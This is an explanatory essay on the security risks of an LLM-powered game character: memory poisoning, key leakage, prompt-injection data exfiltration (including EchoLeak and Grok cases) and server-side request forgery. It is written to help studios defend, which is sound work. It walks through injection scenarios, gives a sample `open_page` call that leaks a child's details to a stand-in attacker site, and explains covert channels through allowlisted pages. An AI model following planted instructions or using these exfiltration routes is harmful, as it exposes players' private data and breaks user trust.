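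To measure the effect, they built a benchmark of cryptocurrency tasks and tested four models, all now old. They put the attacker's instruction either in a tool result or in text presented as a retrieved memory. They used three system prompts: a basic one, one that warned about harmful instructions, and one that required the user to confirm each transaction. The results for 390 attacks on trading tasks show how much the instruction's location mattered for two of the models.

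| System prompt | Claude 3.7 Sonnet, tool result | Claude 3.7 Sonnet, memory | GPT-4o, tool result | GPT-4o, memory |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic | under 1% | 74% | 75% | 96% |
| With warnings | under 1% | 57% | 22% | 74% |
| With confirmation | under 1% | 36% | 4% | 44% |

Patlan and colleagues conclude that models treat their own history as trustworthy and don't check it as they would a web page. But their results could have other explanations. When they put instructions in tool results, they wrapped them in a conspicuous "important message" from a published set of attacks, which newer models may have learned to recognise. They introduced the memories with a neutral phrase. In a log they published, the memory is also tagged as a user message, which would give it more authority than a tool result. A developer who puts memories in the user's part of the prompt, or in the system prompt,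 also gives them too much authority.

The benchmark also starts with the false memory already in place, so it doesn't measure how often an attacker could plant one. *When Agents Remember Too Much* (2026) criticises much of the earlier research on this point. Many attacks assume access to the memory store or to the victim's own assistant, and one that works through web pages needs the assistant to save the same text hundreds of times. This objection is fair for a private assistant but weaker for the innkeeper, because anyone with a game account can add to its shared memory. *MemPoison* (2026) makes a similar point about assistants in Slack and Discord channels, where any member's message can affect later replies to other members.

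In *MemoryDojo*, Yang, Bullwinkel and colleagues (2026) tested the whole process on a current model, OpenAI's GPT-5.6-Luna, with five widely used kinds of memory software. They added one malicious passage to one tool result in the first session, then let the model carry on with ordinary office, travel and banking tasks, with no further action by the attacker. In 15% to 46% of runs, depending on the memory software, the model carried out the attacker's aim in at least one later session. After a second model refined the passage's wording by trial and error, the range rose to 30% to 71%.

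A planted memory has to come up in a later conversation, and the model then has to act on it. The share of later tasks affected is therefore

share affected = share in which the memory comes up × share of those in which the model acts on it

A-MEM fared worst of the five programs. It retrieved the unrefined passage in 90% of later tasks, and the model acted on it in 23% of those, so the passage affected 21% of tasks overall. With Graphiti, the model acted on the passage at almost the same rate once it was retrieved, but Graphiti retrieved it in only 33% of tasks, so it affected only 8%. Storage made less difference because four of the five programs saved some version of the passage nearly every time.

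A memory that already holds a lot of harmless material offers some protection. When Yang and colleagues filled it with about 50 earlier conversations and mixed tasks from different fields, the share affected fell to between 0% and 5%. The innkeeper's memory would hold far more conversations, although the attacker could plant his sentence more than once.

Consumer chatbots have the same weakness. *Hidden in Memory* (2026) reports that outside content could make ChatGPT, Claude and Gemini save invented facts about a user and draw on them in later conversations, which it calls sleeper memory poisoning. It also reports that warnings in the prompt helped only inconsistently. Dash, Ge and colleagues (2026), in *From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory*, found that agents designed to save and retrieve memories more readily were easier to exploit. Designers want game characters to save and retrieve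 memories readily because players enjoy being remembered.

An attacker may be able to write to a model's memory without a model reading his text first. The security researcher Olejnik describes a web page that makes a visitor's browser send ChatGPT a forged request, using the visitor's existing login. The request saves a note to memory, and later chats load it. A studio that lets players edit a character's memories on its website would need to guard against the same attack.

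### One page, two guests

Suppose an attacker publishes a mostly accurate guide to the harvest festival. One paragraph, styled as a notice from the studio, claims that guests must now register on another site, which the attacker runs, and that innkeepers should check each guest's purchases first.

1. In the morning, Ana asks the innkeeper about the festival. The model calls `search_web`, then `open_page` on the guide, and the tool runner adds the whole page to the conversation.
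2. The innkeeper tells Ana the correct date. She thanks it and leaves, with no reason to suspect anything.
3. The game summarises the conversation for the shared memory. The summary states that festival guests must register on the attacker's site after a check of their purchases. It leaves out that this came from a web page.
4. In the evening, Ben asks whether the festival has a horse race. The game searches the memory for "festival", finds the summary and adds it to the prompt.
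5. The model calls `get_player` for Ben's purchases, mentions the horse he bought last week, and sends him to the attacker's site to register.

Ben can't know about the page, and the innkeeper's knowledge of his horse makes the advice more convincing. If he types his password into the site, the attacker gets access to his account. With different instructions, the attacker might have tried to make the innkeeper send out the purchase list through one of its tools.

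Summarising has made the attack harder to spot, because a claim from an unknown website now looks like something the innkeeper knows. Yang and colleagues counted rewritten versions like this as successfully stored, and found that planted instructions also spread into new memories as the model worked. Ben's conversation may add another entry about registration, and the next guest's prompt would then contain two memories that appear to confirm each other.

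Taking down the guide wouldn't fix this. The studio would have to find the stored summary and every later entry that repeats it. Separate memories for each player would have protected Ben from what the innkeeper read for Ana, but not if the innkeeper had also read the guide for him.

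## How access keys leak

An attacker who steals one of the studio's access keys can use the service it unlocks from his own computer, at the studio's expense, without having to persuade the innkeeper of anything. The innkeeper needs at least three keys: one for the model, one for web search and one for the studio's database.

### In the game files and on the network

The worst place to store an access key is in the game itself, because every player then receives a copy. Zotomayor reported that some RyzaChat players extracted character assets and voice clips from the game's files, partly to make their own content. He mentions no key theft, but such files are easy to search for keys because many providers start their keys with fixed characters, such as "AIza" for Google.

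Scrambling the key only delays its discovery. In a Unity forum thread, *Best Way To Encrypt API Key?*, a developer asked how to hide an OpenAI key stored in a script. The reply explained that the game must decrypt the key to use it, so it has to contain everything needed to decrypt it. An attacker can let the game do this and then read the key from memory, or from the request the game sends, without working out the decryption method.

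Web encryption protects a request from strangers on the network, but not from the player, who controls the machine at one end and can make it trust a program that displays the traffic. In *LM-Scout*, Ibrahim, Tuncay and colleagues (2025) used this method to inspect 181 Android apps that use language models. Eleven apps contacted an outside model provider directly and exposed their access credentials. Another 25 added complex encryption of their own to their requests, but the researchers got past it in 11 of those apps by making each app run its own encryption code for them.

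Hiding the key delays attackers for a while. Ibrahim and colleagues skipped 11 apps that checked for tampering, because defeating the checks would have taken real effort. But a popular game may stay on sale for years, and anyone who finds the key can share it with everyone else.

Small developers often have no server to keep a key on. The *NPC-GPT Library*, a package for adding GPT-4 characters to "games and other frontend environments", shows its key being read from an environment variable, a setting stored outside the code. This is sound practice on a server, but a web browser has no such settings. The build tool for a browser game may therefore copy the key into the published file, even if the key doesn't appear in the developer's source code. Demir, Vekaria and colleagues (2026) found in *Keys on Doormats* that 62% of the exposures in websites' JavaScript appeared only in such compiled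 bundles.

A hobbyist who wants one cleverer character in a text adventure made with Inform 7 has much the same choice. They can scramble the access key, ask each player to supply their own, or put it on their website's server and find a way to stop people from calling that server directly.

### Inside the conversation

A key on the studio's server can still leak if it enters the text the model reads. A developer might put the search key in the system prompt and add an `api_key` argument to `search_web`, so that the model copies the key into every tool call. A player who gets the innkeeper to recite its instructions gets the key too. Ibrahim and colleagues extracted system prompts from 34 of the 58 apps that added them on a server.

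*API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, 2026) describes how one key in a model's input can spread to conversation histories, logs, memory stores, generated code and error messages. If an innkeeper character saved the key in memory shared between players, it could appear in another player's conversation.

Error messages can show the model a key that the developer never meant it to see. Some services accept the key as part of the web address, and Leon demonstrates this for Google's Gemini in *Google API Keys Weren't Secrets. But then Gemini Changed the Rules*. When a request fails, networking code often reports the full address it tried. If the tool runner passes that report to the model so that it can try again, the key enters the conversation. Ibrahim and colleagues also found servers that sent the model's complete input back to the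 player, including prompts or keys the server had added.

Access keys can also end up in logs. A server may record full web addresses that contain a key, and a studio investigating an odd reply will probably save the whole prompt, which may contain one too. Support staff, contractors or an outside logging company may be able to read those records, even though the studio would never give them the key.

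A character that can post messages, such as the innkeeper with `post_notice`, might also publish a key by mistake. *Agents in the Wild* (2026) scanned Moltbook, a social network for AI agents, and found that 101 agents had posted 572 strings that matched key formats. The scan matched patterns, so some of the strings may have been expired or invented keys.

### How many keys are exposed

Nobody appears to have counted exposed AI keys in games, but researchers have searched websites, apps and public code for exposed keys. Demir and colleagues examined the landing pages of about 10 million websites and tested the keys they found against 14 services. Leon, who works for Truffle Security, searched an archive of web pages for Google keys. The security companies CloudSEK and Quokka searched mobile apps for Google keys and published their results in *Hardcoded Google API Keys in Top Android Apps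 Now Expose Gemini AI* and *Hundreds of Thousands of Mobile Apps May Now Be Exposing AI Access*, respectively. GitGuardian's *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026* reports that the company found 28.65 million new secrets of all kinds in public code on GitHub in 2025.

| Source | What they searched | What they found |
|---|---|---|
| Demir and colleagues | About 10 million websites, September 2025 | 181 working OpenAI keys |
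| Leon | Archive of web pages, November 2025 | 2,863 working Google keys that opened Gemini |
| CloudSEK | The 10,000 most-installed Android apps | 32 working Google keys that opened Gemini, in 22 apps |
| Quokka | 250,000 mobile apps | A Google key of some kind in 39.5% of apps |
| GitGuardian | Public GitHub commits, 2025 | 1,275,105 leaked secrets for AI services |

The large and small figures count different things. A Google key in an app may give access only to a map, and many leaked keys no longer work. Demir and colleagues found 1,037 strings in OpenAI's format, but only 181 were still valid. GitGuardian's count of leaked keys for AI services rose 81% in a year, which is better evidence of a trend than of how many keys a thief could use. GitGuardian, Quokka and CloudSEK sell security products.

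A harmless key can become sensitive after a game's release. For over a decade, Google told developers that they could safely put keys for services such as Maps in public code. Leon found that if a developer later switched on Gemini in the same Google project, the project's existing keys could also access Gemini, without any warning. A studio could therefore publish a mobile game with a Maps key and expose a paid model a year later by adding an innkeeper character that runs on Gemini in the same project. Google has announced that new keys made in its AI Studio will work only with Gemini by default, and that it will block leaked keys from using Gemini.

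Such a key can also expose data. CloudSEK could use the key from ELSA Speak, an English-teaching app, to list audio files that were probably recordings of users' speech. A studio that stored players' voices the same way would run the same risk.

### What thieves do with a stolen key

Thieves can use a stolen model key themselves or sell access to it. The cloud security company Sysdig (2024) calls this LLMjacking and estimated that heavy use of a cutting-edge model of the time could cost a victim over $100,000 a day. Sysdig says the buyers have included people banned by a model provider and organisations in sanctioned countries.

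Resellers pool many accounts behind a server that Chinese developers call a transfer station. The server forwards each customer's request with one of the pooled keys. Tom's Hardware's *Chinese grey market sells Claude API access at 90% off* reports prices as low as a tenth of the official rate. Stolen keys are only one source of supply. Willison (2026), summarising an investigation by Matt Lenhard, also lists free trials, stolen credit cards and unprotected support bots, through which resellers can use a model without stealing a key.

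Unit 42, Palo Alto Networks' security research team, has handled cases in which thieves connected an exposed key to a transfer station within minutes and ran up nearly $1 million in charges before the victim stopped them. Okta's *Signing in without actually signing in* lists losses of nearly $1 million, $600,000 in credits and $25,000. The largest loss may be from one of Unit 42's cases. Both companies sell protection against this kind of theft, and neither company's figures show the average victim's loss.

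CloudSEK collected three accounts that smaller developers had posted on public forums about their bills. A three-person team that normally spent $180 a month was charged $82,314 in 48 hours. A Japanese company noticed the theft at about $44,000 and paused the service at once, but charges kept accumulating until the next day and reached about $128,000. An alert alone is poor protection if the provider counts usage slowly. A solo developer revoked his keys within ten minutes of a $40 alert, but the billing system ran about 30 hours behind and his final bill was $15,400.

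### Keeping the keys on the server

The remedy is to put no service key in the game at all. For the innkeeper, it would work like this:

1. The player signs in to the studio's server with their game account.
2. The server gives the game a token, a temporary pass that works for that player only and expires after, say, ten minutes.
3. The game sends the player's words with the token. The server checks the token, assembles the prompt and contacts the model provider, using a key that never leaves the server.
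4. The model writes a tool call, such as a search for the festival date. The call contains no key.
5. The tool runner checks the request, adds the search key and sends it to the search company's fixed address.
6. The tool runner removes keys and full web addresses from any result or error before the model reads it.

In some games, the player's machine has to connect directly to a character service, often for speech. In the Convai forum thread *Unity sdk security question*, a developer preparing to publish a game raised a concern that the service's key was built into the game. Convai recommended that the developer's server use the key to create a temporary token for the game to use instead.

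Players can copy a token as easily as a key, but a stolen token is worth far less. If it lasts ten minutes and the server allows six messages a minute at one cent each, a thief can spend at most 60 cents with it. This cap holds only if the server also limits who gets tokens. Ibrahim and colleagues found apps that issued unlimited guest tokens to anyone who asked.

Kenney and colleagues tested a system that adds the key outside the model's reach, as in step 5. They ran 16 checks, and all had the expected result. A request to GitHub succeeded although the program making it held no key, and the key did not appear in replies from three websites that repeat back whatever they receive. In another connection, the system put the key in the wrong part of the request, so the service rejected the request, but nothing leaked. The researchers work for the company that makes the system, and they didn't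 test redirects, which might carry a key to another site.

A model can request harmful actions with a key it can't see. An ElizaOS character sent money to a stranger even though its wallet keys were hidden from the model. Each key should therefore allow as little as possible. The innkeeper's search key should allow only searches, and its database credential should allow it to read age bands and purchases but not change anything. Oversecured's *That AI You Confide in May Be an Open Book* (2026) describes a chatbot app with an OpenAI key and a Google Cloud key in its code. The Google Cloud key gave access to the developer's invoicing system, which the chatbot didn't need.

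Studios should also replace keys regularly, so that a leaked key stops working even if nobody has noticed the leak. The keys that Demir and colleagues found had been public for 12 months on average. If the keys are on a server, the studio can change them without updating the game. If a key is inside the game, revoking it breaks every installed copy until the player updates, which gives the studio a reason to delay.

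After a leak, the studio has to revoke the key with the provider. Deleting the key from a file or a code repository leaves every earlier copy working. The studio should also shut down the server when it retires the game, because Ibrahim and colleagues found two apps that were no longer in Google's store but whose connections to a model still worked.

Moving the keys to a server puts them in one place, which makes that server a better target. KPMG's *AI emerging threat* reports that attackers compromised LiteLLM, a widely used program for routing requests to model providers, so that it stored every key passing through it. A studio that uses such a program has to protect it as carefully as the keys.

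### Players' own keys and local models

A mod maker with no server and no income from the mod may reasonably ask players to supply their own access keys for the model. Then there is no shared key to steal, and if one player's key leaks, the others aren't affected. Glitch9's *Client Side Keys*, a guide to a Unity toolkit, recommends this for tools aimed at other developers, along with narrow permissions and a hard monthly spending limit.

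When players supply their own access keys, they take on the risk. Malware or another mod may be able to read the key on their machine, and they pay for whatever a thief does with it. They also have to trust the mod's maker, because the mod could send the key elsewhere. Some players will type the key into the conversation by mistake, which puts it in the prompt and perhaps in the logs. Many players, especially children, won't have an account with a model provider or know how to set a spending limit.

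Running the model on the player's machine removes the model key and the bill for each message. Conversations can also stay on the machine if the game doesn't send them elsewhere. But the player then has the model, the system prompt and the tool list, and can read or change any of them. Ibrahim and colleagues recovered 22 of the 24 system prompts that apps added on the phone. The two they missed belonged to apps that ran the model locally, probably because they looked for prompts in network traffic and these two never left the phone. Someone searching the phone's files or memory might still find them.

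The innkeeper still needs other keys under either arrangement, because `search_web` requires an account with a search company and `get_player` requires access to the studio's database. The database credential has to stay on the studio's server, which should check who is asking before it returns anything. A check inside the game wouldn't protect other players, because a player can alter a local model to look up any name in the database.

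## How players' data leaves through a tool call

A thief who can't get the studio's database credential may still get players' data, because the game character can look it up for him. He then has to make the character send the data somewhere he can read it, and most of the innkeeper's tools allow this.

### What a character can give away

The innkeeper could give away anything in the text its model reads, and anything its tools can fetch:

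- **Conversations.** Players may tell a friendly character about school, an illness or a quarrel at home.
- **Voice.** A tool call carries text, so the recording itself wouldn't normally leave this way. A transcript could, and so could the model's guess that the speaker is a child.
- **Account details.** `get_player` returns a name, an age band and a list of purchases.
- **Location.** The game may supply a region, or a player may mention their town.
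- **Other players' confidences.** The shared memory keeps what earlier guests told the innkeeper.

Some developers put personal details in the system prompt, where the model has them from the start. Willison (2024) noted that in late 2024 the system prompt of Grok, xAI's chatbot, began with the user's name. It also included the user's region. Embrace the Red's *Security ProbLLMs in xAI's Grok* showed that an attacker could use the region to write hidden instructions that took effect only for users in a chosen place. If a game's system prompt contained the player's age band, an attacker could target children in the same way.

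### Three conditions for theft

*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) describes three conditions that together let an attacker steal data through a language model: the model has access to private data, it reads text that an attacker can influence, and it has a way to send that data out.

The innkeeper meets all three conditions. `get_player` and the shared memory hold private data. Web pages, player names and rumours bring in untrusted text. `post_notice` publishes messages, and `open_page` contacts whatever address the model supplies. Because `open_page` also brings in web pages, it meets two of the conditions on its own. Willison describes a connector between AI assistants and GitHub that met all three. It could read public reports that anyone can file, read private code, and publish the private material in a pull request (a proposed change to a project).

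He also lists more than a dozen products in which researchers had demonstrated such thefts since 2023, including ChatGPT, Slack and Amazon Q. The companies fixed almost all of the flaws promptly, usually by blocking the route through which data could leave, which is often easier than preventing a model from following instructions planted by strangers.

Willison was writing mainly about assistants that work for one person. If such an assistant shows its user the user's own email, nothing has leaked. But the innkeeper talks to thousands of people, so its ordinary replies can also leak data. A player who wants a rival's secrets can supply the untrusted text himself and read the secrets in the innkeeper's reply. A character with a memory shared between players could therefore leak data even if it had no internet tools.

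### The ways out

The simplest way to send data to a website is to put it in the address. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that a website receives the full address of every page someone requests, and commonly logs it. If an attacker gets a model to open an address on his site that ends with a player's name, he can read the name in his log, whatever the page contains and even if it doesn't exist.

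Models vary widely in how often they leak data this way. In *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration*, Rall, Bauer and colleagues (2025) gave each model a store of company documents and a tool for fetching web pages. They asked it to summarise an article that contained hidden instructions to look up a secret and request a web address containing it. They disguised the instructions in many ways and tried each version once per model. xAI's Grok 4 leaked the secret in 72.4% of trials and Alibaba's Qwen3-235B in 28.3%, while OpenAI's GPT-5 nano never did. Size did not reliably predict how often a model leaked. The 70-billion-parameter version of Hermes 4 leaked more often than the 405-billion one (6.0% against 0.1%), but the 235-billion-parameter Qwen3 leaked more often than either. All the models date from 2025, and the researchers added no defences of their own.

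A player whose data leaks through a tool call usually sees nothing wrong. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) asked a model to summarise web pages with instructions planted in the title, description, body or link text. The model sent a request to the researchers' collection server in 423 of 480 runs (88%), and in 95% of those its reply to the user looked harmless. It never contacted the server in 120 runs with clean pages. The 88% rate is weak evidence about current models, because the researchers used a small one, Qwen2.5-7B, gave it a minimal system prompt and placed the secret directly in its input text. The harmless replies matter more for a game, because a moderator who reads only the character's dialogue would miss nearly all such leaks. The studio therefore has to log the tool calls as well.

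An image can carry data out without a tool call. If the model's reply contains an image address, the program displaying the reply may fetch the image automatically, sending whatever the model wrote in the address to the image's server. Embrace the Red reported this problem to OpenAI and Microsoft in early 2023, according to its article *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. Microsoft fixed it in Bing Chat that May by preventing the page from loading images in general. Most games avoid the problem by displaying a character's words as plain text, but a companion app or web version might not.

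Link previews work in much the same way. Some chat apps fetch a linked page as soon as a message arrives, to show the page's title and picture. PromptArmor, a security company, warns that an assistant connected to Slack or Telegram can leak data this way before anybody clicks the link. If the studio copies its guild channel to such an app, a link in one of the innkeeper's notices could also leak data.

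A search query is a less effective way to steal players' data, because it goes to the search company and an attacker normally can't read it. He might see it if the tool searches a site he runs. He could also learn something indirectly if the query determines which of his pages the innkeeper opens next. OpenAI's Deep Research product still checks searches, as well as page visits, for information from the conversation, according to the company's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection*. If it finds any, it either blocks the request or asks the user to confirm it.

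With `post_notice`, the attacker doesn't need a server, because he can join the guild and read the channel. This is also the most visible route, since other members will see the message and may report it, but by then they will have read the data too. To avoid attention, an attacker might have the innkeeper include a detail in an ordinary notice, such as the name of the guild member who just bought an expensive horse.

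The innkeeper might also reveal one player's secrets to another. Suppose a player confides that she is moving house because her parents are divorcing, and the game saves this to the shared memory. Another player later asks the innkeeper what's troubling her. The memory search finds the entry by her name, and the model, whose instructions encourage it to gossip like an innkeeper, tells him. This could happen whether he tricks the character or just asks. The risk is inferred from how shared memory works, as no published test appears to have measured how often characters pass on such confidences. Such a leak would be hard to detect because the log would contain only a conversation, with no suspicious address or tool call.

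### EchoLeak

EchoLeak is a well-documented example of a full chain in a commercial product. Aim Labs, a security research group, found it in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that answers employees' questions using their emails, files and chats. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, describes how it worked:

1. The attacker sent an employee an email that contained instructions and covered several topics employees often ask about.
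2. The employee later asked Copilot about one of those topics. Copilot retrieved the email along with internal material.
3. The model followed the instructions. It picked out the most sensitive information in its text and wrote it into the address of an image in its reply.
4. The employee's browser tried to load the image. Microsoft allowed images only from listed sites, but one of these hosted a Microsoft Teams service that would fetch other addresses on request.
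5. The Teams service contacted the attacker's server and delivered the data.

The employee didn't have to click anything. According to Ravia, the chain could expose anything in Copilot's text, including the chat history, retrieved files, and preloaded details such as the user's name.

*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reports that Aim Labs found the flaw in January 2025, Microsoft fixed it on its servers in May, and both published it on 11 June. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), the entry in a Spanish government database of security flaws, rates its severity 9.3 out of 10. The chain worked on a real product with several defences in place, but only researchers are known to have used it, and Microsoft said that no customers were affected.

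Copilot remained vulnerable after the fix. Microsoft's *CVE-2026-42824* records another flaw, since fixed, that let an outsider obtain information from it. In August 2026, Ars Technica's *Grok exfiltrates user data when malicious instructions are encrypted* mentioned a new attack that made Copilot reveal a password from a user's inbox.

Game studios could easily repeat the mistake in the fourth step. A studio might let the innkeeper contact only its own servers and forget that one of them generates link previews for the forum. If that server fetches any address it receives, the innkeeper can reach the whole web through it.

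### Grok in August 2026

A more recent case involves data much more like what a game holds. *Zero-click Grok data theft*, published by the security company Adversa AI on 20 August 2026, shows a user asking Grok to summarise a web page. Instructions hidden on the page made Grok collect the user's name, rough location, subscription tier and every prompt the user had typed in that conversation. Grok put this data into web addresses and opened those addresses, which sent the data to the researchers' server. The user saw no warning and was not asked to confirm anything.

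Adversa AI reported the flaw to xAI on 3 June and could still reproduce it on 19 August. xAI had acknowledged the report but given no date for a fix. Adversa AI, which sells protection against such attacks, published no success rate, so its demonstration doesn't show how reliably the attack works.

Grok had leaked data before by a different route. In 2024, Embrace the Red found that Grok's iOS app loaded images from outside sites, and that an attacker could use them to steal user data. Every tool a studio adds to a character may create another way for data to leak, and each way needs a check.

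The innkeeper would also have each player's name, rough location, payment tier and conversation. Its data may be more sensitive, because some of the players are children.

### From a planted paragraph to lost data

Suppose the attacker with the harvest festival guide rewrites its false paragraph to claim that festival times differ between guests. The attacker adds that an innkeeper can find each guest's time on a personal page whose address consists of the guest's name, age band and latest purchase.

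1. Cleo, who is 11, asks the innkeeper when the festival starts.
2. The model searches the web, opens the guide and reads the false paragraph.
3. The model calls `get_player` for Cleo. The tool runner allows this, because Cleo is the player in the conversation.
4. The model writes the following tool call, and the tool runner carries it out:

```json
{
  "name": "open_page",
  "arguments": {
    "url": "https://festival-guide.example/times/cleo_fox/under-13/grey-pony"
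  }
}
```

5. The attacker's server logs the address and returns a short page with the correct time.
6. The innkeeper tells Cleo that the festival starts at six.

Cleo got a correct answer, and each tool worked as described. The attacker now knows that a player called cleo_fox is under 13 and has just bought a grey pony. He can find her in the game and start a conversation about ponies.

Limiting the innkeeper to looking up the player it is talking to wouldn't have stopped this attack, because the attacker wanted the details of whoever asked. If the studio had put Cleo's details in the system prompt, the model wouldn't have needed to call `get_player`. If the false paragraph entered the shared memory, the attacker could get later guests' details too.

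### Why a list of permitted pages still leaks

The studio could give the tool runner an allowlist, a fixed list of the only addresses it may contact. Lan and colleagues found that an allowlist blocked every request to the attacker's server in a test of 30 runs. They warn that attackers may still get through by taking over a permitted site or using one that redirects visitors elsewhere.

Suppose the studio closes those gaps too, by permitting exactly 64 pages, with no redirects and nothing added to the addresses. The innkeeper can no longer write Cleo's name into an address, but it can still leak information through its choice of page. The attacker's instructions could assign a meaning to each page, so that opening the page on pumpkins means "under 13" and opening the page on cider means "adult".

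A free choice among *N* pages carries log₂ *N* bits. With 64 pages that is 6 bits, because 2⁶ = 64. A secret of *b* bits therefore needs

*b* ÷ log₂ *N* calls, rounded up.

A 128-bit secret, such as an access key that has slipped into the conversation, needs 128 ÷ 6 = 21.3, so 22 calls. Personal data is often much shorter:

| What the attacker wants | Bits | Calls with 2 pages | Calls with 64 pages | Calls with 1,024 pages |
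|---|---|---|---|---|
| One of four age bands | 2 | 2 | 1 | 1 |
| One account out of a million | 20 | 20 | 4 | 2 |
| A 128-bit secret | 128 | 128 | 22 | 13 |

An allowlist thus protects a long key far better than it protects the fact that a player is a child.

This attack works only if the attacker can see which page the innkeeper opened. He can if he runs one of the permitted sites. He may also be able to if a site displays a visit counter for each page, though visits by other people would make the counts harder to interpret. If all 64 pages are on the studio's own site and only the studio can read the logs, he learns nothing from which page the innkeeper opens.

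The calculation also gives the fewest possible calls and assumes that the model never makes a mistake. If the model picked the right page 95% of the time, it would get all 22 choices right in only about a third of attempts. In tests by Lan and colleagues, a model contacted the collection server in 99% of runs when it could send the whole secret at once, but in about 77% when it had to split the secret across four requests. The share of runs that delivered the whole secret was probably lower, since the 77% includes runs in which only one piece arrived.

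Even after OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from adding anything to the web addresses it received, Radware's researchers got data out in *ZombieAgent*. They supplied a separate address for each letter and digit, then had ChatGPT open the ones that spelled out the data, in order.

OpenAI now lets ChatGPT open an address automatically only if an independent index of the public web already contains it. This prevents the model from automatically opening an address made up for one user, but an attacker can still use a set of indexed pages. daily.dev's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a summary of the Embrace the Red post, mentions this weakness and suggests caching pages and blocking repeat visits within a session.

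A ban on repeat visits would force the attacker to use only one extra call, because the order in which the innkeeper opened 23 different pages out of 64 would still carry more than 128 bits. Stored copies would help more if all players shared them. The attacker's server would then see only the first request for each page, whichever player it came from, until the copy expired. A limit on calls per conversation would also help protect long secrets, but a single call would still be enough to leak the age band.

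### Sharing that needs no attack

Players' data also reaches other companies when everything works as intended. A supplier that hosts the innkeeper's model receives all of the model's input. Since the game resends the conversation each turn, the first message of a 20-turn conversation goes to the supplier 20 times. A speech company may receive the player's voice or the text the character is about to speak, and a search company receives the queries. A studio that hosts its own model, as Epic does for Fortnite, has one fewer supplier.

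A theft sends some players' data to a stranger. Routine sharing affects every player who talks to the character, but the studio chose the recipients and can set terms for what they keep. The studio has to limit routine sharing by sending less data, because a filter that looks for planted instructions won't detect it and an allowlist will include the suppliers the character needs to work.

Software that uses language models often sends more data than a question requires. *Big Help or Big Brother?*, a study from the University of California, Davis, examined browser assistants that answer questions about the page a user is viewing. It reports that some collected the full text of a page, including a patient's medical history, whatever the user asked. The innkeeper would do something similar if the game put each guest's age band and purchases into every prompt, even when the guest only asked about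 the festival.

The studio could instead have its own code read the player's age band and send the supplier only an instruction to keep the jokes clean. The supplier would then receive a hint about the player's age rather than a record of it, and a thief would have less to steal. Children's privacy law may also limit what the studio can share. If a parent asks the studio to delete a child's conversations, its suppliers' copies must be deleted too, so the studio needs to know which companies received them and how long each keeps them.

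## Using the character to reach other machines, get a free model or run up a bill

An attacker may want only to use the innkeeper's connections, not to get players' data. When the innkeeper opens a web page, the request comes from the studio's server. The innkeeper can therefore act as a relay, passing on the attacker's requests so that they appear to come from the studio. The attacker may also want free use of the language model, since the studio pays for every reply.

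### Requests that seem to come from the studio

If a website has blocked a player for copying thousands of its pages, he can ask the innkeeper to open the pages and recite them. The website's logs show only the studio's server. If the site's owner also blocks that server, the innkeeper can no longer look anything up there for honest players.

CERT Coordination Center's *The Librarian does not secure its interface* (2026) describes a commercial product that allowed this. The Librarian is an assistant for email, calendars and documents. Its `web_fetch` tool retrieved outside pages the user chose, so anyone with an account could send requests through the company's servers. A security researcher found the flaw, and the notice mentions no misuse.

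A character is a slow and unreliable relay, because the model takes seconds to reply and may shorten or garble what it has read. It is also a poor way to flood a site with traffic. If each message triggers three page requests, and 100 accounts each send a message every ten seconds, the target receives 30 requests a second. That might overwhelm a fan site on a cheap server, but it would have little effect on a large site, and the attacker could produce far more traffic by renting machines. He gains mainly because complaints about the innkeeper's traffic go to the studio, whose hosting company might even suspend the studio's server.

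Misusing `post_notice` takes no technical skill. A player banned from the guild channel can ask the innkeeper to announce tonight's raid and dictate an insult as the raid's name. A swindler could get a link posted the same way. Guild members may trust a notice from the innkeeper more than one from a stranger, and a screenshot would show the studio's own character posting it. A filter that checks only what players type into the channel will miss these notices.

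### Reaching the studio's own network

Requests to machines inside the studio's network are more dangerous. A game server usually shares that network with machines that hold databases, logs and control panels. These machines have private addresses, often beginning with 10 or 192.168, which work only within the network. The address 127.0.0.1, or "localhost", always refers to the machine making the request. Administrators sometimes leave internal services without a password because nobody outside can connect to them.

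The tool runner can connect to internal addresses that players cannot reach directly. If a player gets the innkeeper to open one, the tool runner fetches the page and the innkeeper describes it to the player. This is called server-side request forgery, which means making someone else's server fetch an address that the attacker could not reach directly.

The security company Mindgard found this flaw in The Librarian too, according to its report *TheLibrarian.io's AI Security Is Checked Out, and Their Disclosure Response Is Overdue*. During a two-day audit, Mindgard asked the assistant whether it could connect to particular ports, the numbered entry points at which a machine's programs listen. The assistant replied that one port had refused the connection and another had accepted it. By probing this way, Mindgard found login pages for a database tool and for a console that starts and stops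 the programs of the company behind The Librarian. An innkeeper that never repeats a page's contents could still help someone map the network if it replies differently to failed and successful connections.

Mindgard also reached the metadata service of the company's cloud provider. A rented cloud machine can usually contact this service at 169.254.169.254 for information about itself, and the answer may include temporary credentials for the customer's cloud account. Some providers answer any request from the machine, while others require a header, which is an extra labelled line sent with the request. The table uses Mindgard's comparison of providers, and its last column assumes a tool that can only request an address.

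| Cloud provider | What the metadata service requires | Could a simple page-fetching tool read it? |
|---|---|---|
| Amazon, older version | Nothing beyond the address | Yes |
| Amazon, newer version | A session token, which takes a different type of request to obtain | No |
| Microsoft Azure | A header | No |
| Google Cloud | A header | No |
| Hetzner, DigitalOcean, Alibaba | Nothing beyond the address | Yes |

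A required header doesn't help if the attacker can set headers. SecurityWeek's *ChatGPT Vulnerability Exposed Underlying Cloud Infrastructure* reports that Jacob Krut, a security engineer, reached Azure's metadata service through ChatGPT in 2025. He used Actions, a feature for connecting a customised version of ChatGPT to outside services, and obtained an access token that could have let him into the cloud infrastructure OpenAI uses. According to eSecurity Planet's *ChatGPT Exploited Through SSRF Flaw in Custom GPT Actions*, the feature let users configure authentication headers, which is probably how he supplied the header Azure requires. OpenAI rated the flaw high severity and quickly fixed it.

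Krut supplied the address himself when he defined the tool, so he didn't have to persuade a model of anything. MITRE's *CVE-2025-66201* (2025) records a similar flaw in LibreChat, a ChatGPT-like program. A game platform that let outside creators define internet tools for their characters would run the same risk. Epic has largely avoided this risk in Fortnite by not letting ordinary creators contact outside services.

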